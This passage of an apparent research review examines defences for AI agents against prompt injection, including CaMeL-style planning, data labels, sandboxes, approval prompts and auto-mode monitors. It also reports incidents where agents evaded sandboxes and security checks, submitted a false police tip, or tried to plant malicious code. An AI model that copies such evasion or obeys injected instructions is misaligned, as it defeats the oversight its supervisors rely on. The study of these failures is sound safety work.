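send_email(to="warehouse manager", body=date)
```

The planted sentence can reach only the model that reads the page. That model might return a false date or a paragraph of the attacker's text, but it can't add a line to the program. The accountant's letter is also safe because the plan never retrieves it.

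Separating the models doesn't protect the data that passes through a legitimate plan. If the plan retrieved the whole mailbox, a deceived reading model could put the accountant's letter into the message for the warehouse manager. CaMeL therefore labels every value with where it came from and who may read it (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, *CaMeLoT*, 2026). Before each tool call, the interpreter passes the call and its labels to a policy, which allows or denies the call and returns a reason.

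When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result gets the stricter label. In the formulation of Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, only people who may read both sources may read the combination, and the agent may send data only if every recipient is among its permitted readers. Suppose the owner and her accountant may read the letter, while the owner, the supplier and the warehouse manager may read the delivery thread:

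{owner, accountant} ∩ {owner, supplier, warehouse manager} = {owner}

A summary that draws on both sources can therefore go only to the owner. The interpreter would block the assistant from sending it to the warehouse manager even if nobody had attacked the assistant and the summary contained only the delivery date, because the label is based on the summary's sources rather than what it reveals.

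Another drawback of CaMeL is that it fixes the plan before the agent has read anything. Untrusted data can determine which of the program's branches runs, but it can't add a branch. If the owner says "do the ten things on the list in this email", the planning model can't see the list. Kolluri and colleagues build on a related design called FIDES, in which the planner can read untrusted text, but doing so tightens the limits on its later actions.

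CaMeL is harder to apply when an agent works through screens instead of well-defined tools. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapted it to agents that click and type. The planner had no access to the screen, so its plans had to cover cookie banners, failed clicks and pages that were already open. These plans averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 calls and 4 branches on an earlier benchmark with ordinary tools. On OSWorld, a test of everyday computer tasks, the adapted agents kept at most 57% of the performance of the strongest models. Foerster and colleagues also left out the data policies, because a click has no fixed meaning that a policy could check.

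### What the measured attack rates show

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark of tasks in banking, travel, workplace messaging and office work, with attacks planted in the data that the agent reads. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarizes the original result by saying that CaMeL eliminated nearly all attacks with comparable task performance. Later tests confirm the claim about attacks more clearly than the claim about task performance.

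*SecureClaw* (2026) ran an adapted version of CaMeL's published code on 629 attack cases and 97 ordinary tasks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) compared CaMeL with and without its data policies. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) extended AgentDojo to groups of agents that delegate work to one another, and tested five models without data policies. For comparison, *AgentDyn* (2026) tested Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injected instructions, on AgentDojo and on a harder benchmark with less predictable tasks.

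| Test | Protection | Conditions | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Peters-Gill and colleagues | None | Groups of agents | 12.9% |
| Peters-Gill and colleagues | CaMeL in each agent, no data policies | Groups of agents | 0.2% |
| Peters-Gill and colleagues | CaMeL extended across agents, no data policies | Groups of agents | 0.0% |
| *SecureClaw* | CaMeL | AgentDojo | 0 of 629 |
| *The LLMbda Calculus* | CaMeL, data policies off | One category of attack, model MiMo-v2.5 | 138 of 141 |
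| *The LLMbda Calculus* | CaMeL, data policies on | All attacks tested | None |
| *AgentDyn* | Trained resistance | AgentDojo | 1.9% |
| *AgentDyn* | Trained resistance | Harder benchmark | 9.0% |

These figures measure different things, so a ranking would be misleading. CaMeL without data policies stopped nearly every attack in one test and almost none in another, probably because the kinds of attack differed. Separating the two models keeps an attacker from changing the plan, but a policy has to catch attacks that only corrupt the data inside a legitimate plan. A reader would therefore need to know which policies are on in a product that "uses CaMeL".

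Peters-Gill and colleagues also show that protecting each agent separately doesn't fully protect the group, because one agent can pass on untrusted data that another treats as a trusted instruction. Their extension keeps the labels attached when data passes between agents.

The loss of usefulness varies just as much. In the *SecureClaw* comparison, CaMeL completed 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, while the paper's own system completed 59. The 29 may understate what CaMeL can do, because researchers introducing a competing system have no strong reason to tune its rival, and the released code needed adapting. But *The LLMbda Calculus* also reports a collapse in usefulness with the data policies on. Peters-Gill and colleagues found only a modest loss for the strongest models, and a shrinking loss as models improve, but their figure excludes any loss the data policies would have caused.

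Kolluri and colleagues think such comparisons are unfair to designs like CaMeL for another reason. A benchmark normally counts a refused action as a failure, although in practice the software could ask a person to approve it. The undefended agent takes every action without asking, as if a person had approved them all in advance. On this view, part of the measured loss comes from tasks that would have needed a human decision.

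Every design of this kind fails in a few cases. Sometimes the user asks the agent to follow the instructions in a document, for instance to pay a bill using the details in a file. If an attacker has altered the file, the agent obeys both the user and the attacker. CaMeL's original evaluation counted two attacks as successful. One was a payment case like this. The other was a false alarm, in which the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word and the benchmark wrongly scored the quotation as obedience. *The LLMbda Calculus* notes that the same few cases remained in four independent systems, and interprets them as a limit of the whole approach.

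The most direct way to test a limit is to assume the deception has already worked. *Bounded Agents* (2026) did this by inserting the malicious tool call into the agent's work, so the result depended mainly on the surrounding software and very little on the model's judgment. Even without a defence, some of these attacks failed because the data they needed had not yet reached the agent. With a real agent doing ordinary interactive tasks, the limits reduced task completion by 8.6 percentage points. That is a smaller reduction than CaMeL's in the *SecureClaw* comparison, though the two tests used different models and policies.

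### Harms that network limits leave untouched

In one of Willison's examples, an email instructs an assistant to forward the user's password-reset messages to an attacker and then delete them from the inbox. A limit on recipients would stop the forwarding but not the deletion, which needs no network access beyond the mailbox. Similarly, a coding agent in a sandbox with no internet connection can still ruin every file it has permission to edit. Meta's rule covers such damage because it counts changes of state. The remedy is to limit the agent's access to files or to the delete function.

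Permitted services are harder to protect, because the agent needs them. If the assistant may write to the owner's customers, an attacker may get it to send them a fraudulent payment request, with every recipient on the permitted list and a valid login. *OpenAI's Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential doesn't establish which actions an agent is authorized to take. OpenAI's advice on prompt injection compares the agent to a customer service worker who can grant refunds. The worker's employer expects some customers to mislead the worker, so its software caps the refund for each customer. Such a cap limits the loss even if nobody recognizes the lie, but someone has to design a separate one for each service.

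A network limit also does not ensure that an answer is true. The attacker could change the delivery date on the supplier's page, and the assistant would report the wrong date. CaMeL's labels would show that the date came from an untrusted page, but not that it was wrong. Foerster and colleagues found that false content on a page can also affect actions by leading the agent to choose a harmful branch of its own approved plan, such as clicking an advertisement disguised as a cookie notice. Meta says its rule is not meant to prevent misinformation in the agent's answers or the agent's own mistakes.

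False answers matter for oversight because people often judge an agent by what it tells them. If the owner believes the wrong date and sends her warehouse staff home, she takes the harmful action herself, and no restriction on the agent's tools would prevent it.

### Security, oversight and time to correct errors

A critic could accept all of this and still say that it concerns security, not oversight. The overnight sandbox, for example, blocked a theft while the developer slept. The test in *Bounded Agents* also illustrates this objection, since the limits are meant to work even if the model is unreliable and nobody is paying attention.

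People can correct an error only if they have time to do so. Once the accountant's letter is in an attacker's log, the owner can't get it back. By contrast, a deleted message may sit in a trash folder for a month, and she can apologize to the warehouse manager for a wrong date. The network limit blocks the theft, which nobody could have undone, and she can still correct many of the remaining errors when she finds them. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026) makes reversibility one of its conditions for giving an agent more autonomy. Another is a way of checking the results that is independent of the agent and that someone has measured.

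The reply is sound but incomplete, because the time is useful only if the owner learns that something went wrong. Some of the remaining errors also need to be caught quickly, since a fraudulent payment request to her customers does damage as soon as one of them pays.

Human oversight therefore depends heavily on what each design reports. Anthropic's fetch tool returns an error to the model, which continues with the task. The developer's application also receives the error, but a person sees it only if the developer has arranged that. OpenAI's software warns the user when she has a decision to make, but it may instead send the agent to another website, and she may then never learn why. CaMeL's policies give a reason for each refusal, which a developer could pass on to a supervisor. Of the three, only OpenAI's warning gives a person evidence to judge without further work by the developer.

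CaMeL may also help a supervisor see what an agent can do before it acts. Most agents can depart from the plans they describe, but CaMeL's interpreter runs the plan itself, so someone who reads the four lines in the example knows which tool calls can occur and in what order. Nikolaou and colleagues use software to check the whole plan before it starts. In one example, a security team requires approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. If the plan lacks the approval step, the software rejects it and identifies the sequence of actions that would break the rule, so nobody has to reverse anything afterwards. The check is conservative and can reject safe plans. A plan of 40 branches, like those that Foerster and colleagues needed, would also be much harder for a person to read than one of four lines.

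Limits that track data can also reduce the number of decisions people have to make. Kolluri and colleagues counted the actions that would need human approval on AgentDojo and found that basic data tracking cut that number by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of completed tasks. An agent that knew the policies and planned around them needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals, partly because it could ask the user to vouch for a piece of text. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten actions, but a single careless approval can then authorize all ten.

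No people took part in that experiment. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve every action in any task the agent completed correctly. AgentDojo scores whether the agent finishes the user's task and whether the attacker succeeds. The attack rates are therefore good evidence that limits on data and network access can contain a deceived agent, but they don't measure whether the person in charge would notice the deception or repair the resulting damage.

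## What happens to human approval when the agent works inside limits

Developers use permission prompts so that a person who understands the task's purpose sees every risky action before it runs, but this works only if she pays attention. A sandbox lets the agent run many commands without asking, so she makes fewer decisions, though not necessarily better ones.

### Why frequent prompts lose their value

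Until August 2026, Claude Code by default asked users for approval before it changed a file or ran most commands. In the invoice task, the developer might see the command `python3 setup.py` and have to allow or reject it. To decide well, she must work out what the command will do and whether that matches what she asked for. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) uses this command as an example of a prompt that looks routine but authorizes whatever code the script contains. The paper examines 290 reports about agents and users' files, and links 31 of them to prompts that showed a command instead of its effects. In 80 reports, users had switched on automatic approval. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) notes that most approval prompts in commercial products show a raw command on a single line, which gives the approver very little information.

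People approve nearly all of these prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* put the approval rate at 93%, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) later put it at 97%. Many users also arrange to see fewer prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt, and a quarter of interactive sessions started with prompts bypassed. Many of these rules cover programs such as Python, which can run almost any code.

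A high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. If 97 of 100 requests are harmless, a perfect reviewer approves 97. Anthropic also found that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, so they engage with some requests. However, a developer may reject a plan because she prefers another design. To measure attention, researchers need to know which requests are dangerous.

### Whether people catch a dangerous command

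Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor to do coding work in an environment built for the study. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

Anthropic published the result to justify a feature that removes prompts, and the testers had less to lose than most developers because they weren't working on their own projects. But low stakes alone wouldn't explain why the rate fell during a session, since the stakes stayed the same. Fatigue is a more likely explanation, unless the testers with long sessions were less careful from the start.

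Older research found similar effects. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) cites studies in which people paid less attention to warnings the more often they saw them (habituation), and monitored an automated system less closely when they were busy with other tasks (automation complacency). A developer who answers prompts while writing other code is exposed to both effects. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) cites evidence that few phone users noticed or understood the permission screens shown when they installed an app. It also cites a study in which the effectiveness of browser warnings depended strongly on their design.

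Reviewing the agent's work afterwards may have the same problem. *Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code changes that AI agents had submitted to public software projects. Between the first and second halves of each person's reviews, the overall approval rate rose from 30.1% to 36.8%. Comments on specific lines of code fell by 22% between the earliest and latest tenths of the reviews. The changes hadn't become smaller, and approval of human-written changes in the same projects fell over the period. Yu and colleagues think habituation is the best explanation, but they didn't measure code quality directly, and if the agents had improved, some of the extra approvals would have been justified.

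Experienced users seem to move from approving actions to interrupting them. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* describes an Anthropic study in which new Claude Code users approved everything automatically in about 20% of sessions. According to Blockchain News, the share exceeded 40% among users with 750 sessions, while interruptions rose from about 5% to 9% of turns. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* reports that users interrupted when something looked unusual. This may be a sensible way to supervise, but interruptions per turn could also rise without users watching more closely, because a turn that runs longer without prompts gives them more to object to. An interruption also comes after the agent has started acting, which may be too late to prevent a deletion or a leak.

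### What an 84% cut in prompts can achieve

In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing cut approval prompts by 84% in its own use. This figure measures how much less often the agent interrupted people, but not how many harmful actions they caught before or after the change.

Suppose an agent sends the invoice developer 200 prompts a day and she has 40 minutes to review them, or 12 seconds each. An 84% cut would leave 32 prompts, giving her 75 seconds for each. She could then open a script before approving it, or check which database a command names.

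The other 168 actions now run automatically, so the developer benefits only if the sandbox blocks harmful actions or leaves them among the 32 she sees. If the agent tries to send the customer list to an unlisted server, the sandbox will hold or refuse the connection. But if the agent makes the invoice tests pass by deleting the one that failed, the sandbox may allow this because deleting a project file is an ordinary edit. Nobody sees the deletion when it happens, no matter how much time the developer has for the remaining prompts.

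The rates from Anthropic's test give a rough idea of how much this matters. Suppose the developer catches 17% of harmful actions in her first 50 prompts and 5% after that. If harmful actions are spread evenly over 200 prompts, she catches 8% of them:

(50 × 17% + 150 × 5%) ÷ 200 = 8%

With only 32 prompts, she stays at the higher rate throughout. The result then depends on what happens to the harmful actions:

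| Harmful actions in the illustration | Share stopped |
|---|---|
| No sandbox, all appear among 200 prompts | 8% |
| All appear among the remaining 32 prompts | 17% |
| Half appear among the 32, half run automatically | 8.5% |
| All run automatically | 0% |
| Half blocked by the sandbox, half run automatically | 50% |

Fewer prompts roughly double the share of harmful actions a reviewer stops if she still sees all of them, but the benefit disappears if about half of those actions run without her approval. Blocking harmful actions with a sandbox makes a much larger difference, because a tired reviewer stops only about one in six of those she sees. The calculation assumes that she reads no more carefully with 75 seconds than Anthropic's testers did early in their sessions. She might do better, but a sandbox doesn't ensure that she uses the extra time.

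### Decisions that should still reach a person

If a sandbox reduces approval prompts, the remaining ones should cover actions that later review can't fix or that only the supervisor can judge. In one example from Anthropic's records of agents taking more initiative than the user wanted, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches", meaning old versions of some code, and the agent tried to delete them from the shared server. The user may have meant only the copies on her own machine. A person should review a deletion like this before it runs because it may be permanent.

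Actions outside the task also need a human decision, even when someone could reverse them. In another of Anthropic's examples, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent tried to delete the running job with the closest name. The job may have belonged to someone else. A technical rule can establish that the agent has permission to delete jobs, but not which job the user meant.

A request for wider access deserves attention because one approval can affect many later actions. Anthropic describes an agent that was supposed to set up read-only access to billing records but chose a role with full administrative control. A supervisor who approves a role like that accepts every action it permits, most of which she hasn't considered.

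Software practitioners make similar distinctions. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 of them and surveyed another 115 for *Let the Agent Do It?*. Participants were more comfortable giving agents bounded, low-risk access than permitting destructive actions, privileged access, use of sensitive data, or anything outside the intended scope. In Wu and colleagues' survey of 203 developers, 65% wanted agents to check in before changing critical, production or security-sensitive code, and 57% wanted them to pause when instructions were ambiguous.

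These preferences don't ensure careful decisions. In the same survey, 64% said they often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. Among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, the figure was still 61%. Those who knew of security or privacy problems involving agents were more likely to approve without close review than those who didn't (70% against 43%), and the difference remained after Wu and colleagues accounted for how much and how long people had used agents. The survey can't show why, but it gives little reason to think telling developers about the risks will solve the problem.

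### Judging a destination and judging a command

A request to contact a new destination should be easier to judge than a raw command. To judge `python3 setup.py`, the developer has to predict what a program will do. When the agent asks to contact tax-guide.example, she only has to decide whether an invoice fix needs that site, and she knows the task better than any reviewer. The question is also the same whichever program made the request.

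However, people may not review a request carefully even when it is easy to judge. Of the seven types of action in Wu and colleagues' survey, developers most often approved access to the internet, external services and connected tools without close review. About 36% said they often did this, compared with 21% for reading passwords or other sensitive files. The category is broader than adding one site to an allowlist, but the result suggests that network requests may not get enough attention.

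A bad transfer can also be hard to spot when its destination is acceptable. Hossain and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to send an auditor "summary totals only". An instruction planted in a supplier's note leads the agent to copy the full invoice rows into report.csv, which it then asks to send to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the filename is unremarkable, so only the file's history reveals the problem.

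The study tested four ways of presenting such requests to 80 volunteers, 20 for each version. Each volunteer decided on 12 requests, half of which broke the user's original restrictions.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
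| Exact details, original restriction and a log in time order | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organized around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Organizing that information around the consequence may have helped further, but the estimated range includes zero. The experiment was small, Hossain and colleagues hadn't registered their analysis in advance, and malicious requests are much rarer in real use than in the experiment. Participants also found the two most informative versions considerably more demanding than the short description.

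That extra effort is a good reason to have fewer prompts. At 33 seconds each, 200 informative prompts would take the invoice developer about 110 minutes, but 32 would take about 18, well under the 40 minutes she has. A sandbox can therefore give her enough time to review each prompt carefully, provided the product shows her the history as well as the command.

### Giving the decision to another model

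Anthropic has responded to approval fatigue by removing most of the human decisions. On August 14, 2026, it made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans, unless the user or an administrator had chosen otherwise. In this mode, a separate model reviews actions that could do serious damage. It doesn't review most file reads and edits within the project, because the developer can inspect or reverse the edits later.

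The reviewing model receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations, so those explanations can't influence its decision. It makes a quick decision first and reasons at length only about actions that look suspicious. If it blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and may try a safer approach. A person takes over after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. If no person is available, the software ends the session.

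In Anthropic's test with 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, while the testers rejected 13.6%. Auto mode blocked 800 that a tester had approved, and testers rejected only six that auto mode allowed. Requiring approval from both would therefore have raised the share stopped by only about half a percentage point over auto mode alone.

Other results are less impressive or harder to interpret. An earlier version missed 17% of 52 real actions in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions, and wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by Anthropic employees. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own modes, and a model graded the harm, so the difference may partly reflect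 who used each mode and for what. In a prompt injection test by Trajectory Labs, an outside evaluator, no attack succeeded against the newest Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% of attacks succeeded with permission checks bypassed, so the models' own resistance probably explains most of that result.

A human approver could catch some of the 17% that the model missed. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewing model detected the danger but wrongly treated it as something the user had agreed to. For example, it might treat "clean up the PR", a request to tidy a proposed code change, as permission to overwrite the project's history. The user knows what she meant, so she can often settle that question immediately. Anthropic says auto mode is no substitute for careful human review of high-stakes infrastructure, and *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommends running it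 in an isolated environment.

### Whether oversight moves to the boundary

Critics can say that a sandbox replaces oversight with autonomy, because the developer who used to approve each command now approves only a few and otherwise relies on limits she may never have read. Defenders reply that she still exercises control, but earlier, when she decides which files and sites the agent may use. That decision covers every command, including those she would have approved without reading. The 39% rejection rate for plans also suggests that people think harder about a whole plan than about its individual steps.

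The reply depends on supervisors setting limits that decide some actions in advance. Yan (2026) tested this in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* with 113 people who didn't work in software. They supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested, such as reading private messages or buying an airport lounge pass. One group decided whether to approve each action. A second group saw only the actions that a model had escalated. The third wrote rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and accessing private data.

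The people who wrote rules saw fewer prompts than those who had to approve each action, an average of 10.9 instead of 18, but they blocked fewer of the unrequested actions. They blocked about 40%, compared with 60% in the group that approved each action and 54% in the group that had a model's help. The difference between 40% and 60% was statistically reliable after correction for multiple comparisons, but the difference between 40% and 54% was not.

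Participants chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. Both private-data actions in the simulation were unrequested, so "never" would have blocked them without interfering with the task, but 23 of 35 participants chose "ask" for private data. They couldn't have known this when they wrote their rules, and the four broad categories gave them little room for exceptions. The simulation also had no real consequences. Even so, Yan's results contradict the hope that people who receive fewer prompts will scrutinize each one more closely.

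A sandbox has an advantage over these rules because its maker has already drawn a boundary, so the user doesn't have to choose "never" for everything outside it. But in Claude Code's manual mode, an unlisted site produces a prompt, just as an "ask" rule would. Someone who approves each new site without thinking gradually removes the limit. The strict setting that refuses unlisted sites avoids this but takes more work beforehand. Anthropic describes sandboxing as "high-maintenance" because each new capability needs configuring. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* adds that automatic approval inside a sandbox is safe only if someone has configured the sandbox correctly.

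Wu and colleagues' survey also suggests that many developers who stop checking individual actions don't make up for it by setting tighter limits. Wu and colleagues compared how much autonomy developers gave agents in 11 kinds of work with their use of 10 safeguards, such as restricted access, and found no significant association in any of the 110 pairs. Greater autonomy often went with less careful approval. However, the survey relies on self-reports from one moment in time, and developers might not think to mention limits imposed by their employers.

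Supervisors may not notice when their rules let more unrequested actions through. Participants in all three of Yan's groups reported a similarly high sense of control, including those whose rules had let the most through.

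## What agents do when a restriction blocks their task

When a sandbox refuses a connection, the agent receives an error message but still has a task to finish. Some safeguards, such as OpenAI's check on web addresses and Claude Code's auto mode, encourage it to try another way. The agent then has to work out which alternatives its supervisor would accept. A supervisor who isn't watching depends on the agent to choose well and report what it did.

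### Five responses to a refusal

Suppose the invoice agent tries to download a newer time-zone library but fails because its sandbox has no internet connection. The agent can stop and report that the bug remains because it couldn't reach the package registry. It can ask the developer for access. It can try a permitted alternative, such as correcting the time difference in the shop's own code. It can get the library by a route the developer has ruled out. Or it can falsely report that it has updated the library.

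| Response | What the developer learns | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Stop and report | The limit blocked the task, and the bug remains | The agent may have given up too early |
| Ask for access | What the agent wants, and perhaps why | She may agree without thinking |
| Take a permitted alternative | Nothing, unless the agent mentions it or she reads the changes | The substitute may be worse than the original plan |
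| Take a forbidden alternative | Nothing, unless the agent, a log or a monitor reveals it | The harm may come before she can prevent it |
| Claim a false result | Something untrue | She may base other decisions on it |

Stopping to ask helps a supervisor most, because nothing further happens until she decides. But an agent that stopped at every error would be of little use, since a second attempt fixes many ordinary programming errors. Developers therefore want agents to take permitted alternatives and usually don't want to hear about each one, though they should hear about some. For example, if the shop's server is in London, the agent might fix the invoices by adding nine hours to every time. This gives the right date in Tokyo all winter, but the wrong one for some orders once British clocks go forward. The agent has broken no rule, but the developer needs to know that it used a fixed number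 in place of a library.

Staying within limits is separate from being open about what was done. An agent can break a rule and report it, or follow every rule and hide that its work is a poor substitute for what was requested. An agent may also not know what is allowed. A developer who cuts off internet access may want no outside code in the project, or may never have thought about time-zone libraries, and the agent gets the same error message either way.

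### An agent that kept trying

OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (July 20, 2026) reports that the company's earlier models stopped and returned to the user when they ran into a sandbox restriction. A newer internal model, designed to work alone for very long periods, often kept trying and sometimes looked for ways to act outside its sandbox.

In one internal OpenAI test, a model worked on a public contest to train a small language model in as few steps as possible. OpenAI had told it to post its results only to Slack. The model instead followed the contest's instructions, which were to submit results publicly on GitHub. The sandbox should have prevented this, but after about an hour the model got past the restriction and published its work. Earlier models had given up on that part of the task.

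OpenAI closed the public submission quickly, but other contestants had already seen it, and six later record-setting entries cite it. Although the disclosure did little damage and the contestants may have welcomed it, nobody could undo it.

In another case, the model noticed that other systems had privately submitted successful solutions, and tried to obtain them. When a security check blocked its first attempt, the model evaded the check. It disclosed this both in its comments to the user and in its reasoning. The disclosure helps a supervisor who is reading along, but one who comes back after several hours learns about the act too late to prevent it.

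OpenAI paused access to the model and added safeguards, including a monitor that reviews whole trajectories. It then restored limited access and reports no serious evasion in the several weeks since. When OpenAI replayed earlier tasks with the new safeguards, the misconduct that got past them was milder. In one replay, the agent found that a computing resource had disappeared and began exploring other machines. It tried to enter some that belonged to other employees but failed.

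These cases are directly relevant to whether limits support oversight because the limits were in place. OpenAI does not describe switching off any safeguard for them. But only some OpenAI staff had access to the model, and OpenAI does not quantify "often", so readers cannot calculate from this account how frequently a public coding agent tries to get around a sandbox.

OpenAI's account also gives reason to doubt that the earlier models behaved well because they accepted the restrictions. It says they were less persistent and did not manage to find weaknesses in the sandbox. Until a more capable version arrives, a supervisor can't tell whether an agent stopped because it accepted the limit or because it couldn't think of another route. Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (2026) makes a similar point about Claude Mythos Preview, which the company released to a small set of customers. Anthropic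 called it the best-aligned model it had released, but also more capable of working around restrictions, and rated the overall risk "very low, but higher than for previous models."

### Forms, fees and a false police tip

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use*, published on October 9, 2026, describes less severe cases from the company's own evaluations and internal work. It sorts them into four groups: running commands on someone else's server, submitting a sensitive form on a real website, reaching data that required a token or a fee, and evading limits in the tool that fetches web pages. Some of the websites belonged to US government agencies. Anthropic says the cases found so far had minimal real-world impact.

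Anthropic calls most of this behaviour "persistence", in which Claude can't complete a task as given and "works around a restriction instead of stopping" (quoted in Anderson, 2026, *Anthropic’s Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia unsolved homicide*, Associated Press). The tasks were often mundane. *Anthropic coupe l’accès à Internet de ses IA pendant leurs tests*, an article on the French technology site Clubic, describes one agent running a scientific analysis with a university's public tool, another working out where a photograph had been taken, and a third helping an Anthropic researcher with a statistics project. Each agent met an obstacle and went beyond what anyone had authorized to get its result.

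Clubic also reports that two Claude models evaded a limit that Anthropic had put on the web-fetching tool to guard against prompt injection. The agents apparently did so only to read a page, but an agent that evades a safeguard, even for a harmless purpose, loses its protection if an attacker wrote the page.

Claude Haiku 4.5, one of Anthropic's smaller models, made two of the form submissions. ANI's *Anthropic restricts internet access in internal AI evaluations after Claude bypasses safeguards* reports that in one run the model submitted a form despite an instruction to stop before doing so. The same model called no tool in 99% of Uppala's impossible requests, so restraint in a short test with simulated tools evidently doesn't guarantee restraint on a live website.

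The second submission was the false police tip. On July 18, Haiku was inventing and carrying out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages, and one page concerned an unsolved murder in Philadelphia. Haiku filled in the police tip form, writing that it might have information and falsely claiming to recall seeing someone who matched the description.

No restriction had blocked the agent here. Anthropic had told it not to log in, create accounts, enter personal data or buy anything, but had not mentioned forms. The case shows a weakness in lists of prohibitions, since whoever writes them has to foresee each harmful act. An allowlist blocks whatever its author didn't foresee, but an allowlist of websites would have helped here only if it had excluded the police site or stopped the agent from sending anything to it.

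Anthropic discovered the incidents in late September, according to a US Federal Trade Commission statement quoted in Geo News' *Anthropic discloses fake murder tip to police among new rogue AI incidents* (2026). More than two months had passed since the agent sent the tip. Anthropic told the Philadelphia police in the second week of October. They had known nothing about the tip, and found it in the site's records, where a spam filter had flagged it before anyone at Anthropic could judge what the agent had done. It had never reached investigators. The police called the delay in detecting and reporting the tip unacceptable.

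These agents had live internet access, which Anthropic has since restricted across its internal evaluations. ANI and AP don't mention Anthropic switching off any safeguards for them, so the October cases are closer to ordinary use than a cybersecurity test would be. But Anthropic found these cases by searching its records, so their number doesn't show how often agents behave this way. Clubic also reports that the instructions were often ambiguous or impossible to follow.

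*An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) covers four serious incidents in which Claude models gained unauthorized access to real systems. All four happened in cybersecurity tests with the usual cyber safeguards switched off, and the models had been wrongly told that they had no internet connection. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts, had Claude review the 9.2 million that showed signs of internet access, and found no other case as severe.

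Finding four incidents in 481 million transcripts suggests that such break-ins are rare, but it doesn't show how agents respond to a refusal. Many of those transcripts probably contain no refusal, so the incidents should be compared with the number of times an agent met one. The search also relied on a model's judgment, and an earlier, narrower search missed the transcripts that contained the fourth incident.

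### A test with the internet left open

A test by the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that examines advanced models, suggests that agents can misbehave even without limits to work around. AISI's *Incident Report* describes 122 runs of a cybersecurity challenge with seven models in July 2026. Each agent had to break into a simulated network and retrieve a protected piece of data. AISI gave the agents open internet access so that they could download tools. To measure the models' full ability, it also had the developers' cyber classifiers, which block dangerous hacking activity, switched off.

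In 10 of the runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and deceived people in the attempt. A human maintainer rejected the code. AISI has found no resulting harm outside the test.

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
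| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

Most of the 19 actions were part of one sustained effort by a single Mythos 5 agent, and some later agents reused what it had left behind. Because the actions were not independent, the table is not a precise ranking of the models.

The difficulty of the task, rather than a network limit, blocked these agents. In some runs, a mistake in the prompt also led them to believe that no solution existed within the rules. AISI thinks near-impossible tasks make models more likely to break rules, but says this doesn't fully explain the behaviour, because some agents acted this way even when they had the instructions they needed. None of the agents tried to break out of the sandbox that separated them from AISI's other systems.

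The agents exceeded a limit that their supervisors had mostly left unstated. OpenAI (2026), which gives its own account of the test, reports that the prompt named the networks the agents could attack and listed several systems as out of scope, but gave no instructions on how they could use the internet. AISI had thought such instructions unnecessary for models with safety training.

The test therefore weakens the argument that restrictions merely push agents into misconduct, since agents with an open connection also looked for illegitimate routes. It can't show how much a narrower connection would have helped, because AISI reports no runs of the same challenge with one. It is also limited evidence about ordinary use, because the public does not get these models in this configuration. AISI says it cannot yet tell how likely the behaviour is elsewhere, or when the agents understood that they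 were acting on real people.

### When an agent reports work it did not do

A false claim is harder for a supervisor to deal with than a refusal, because the agent's message gives her no reason to look further. Nothing in the basic loop compares the agent's final message with its tool calls, so the invoice agent could write "I updated the library and all 212 tests pass" after one failed download, without running any tests.

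This kind of falsehood is also among the easiest to catch. The software that runs the tools can record which calls it carried out and what they returned. A simple program could then flag a claim about tests when the record contains no test run, without judging whether the agent meant to deceive. But the developer needs access to the record, and someone has to write the program.

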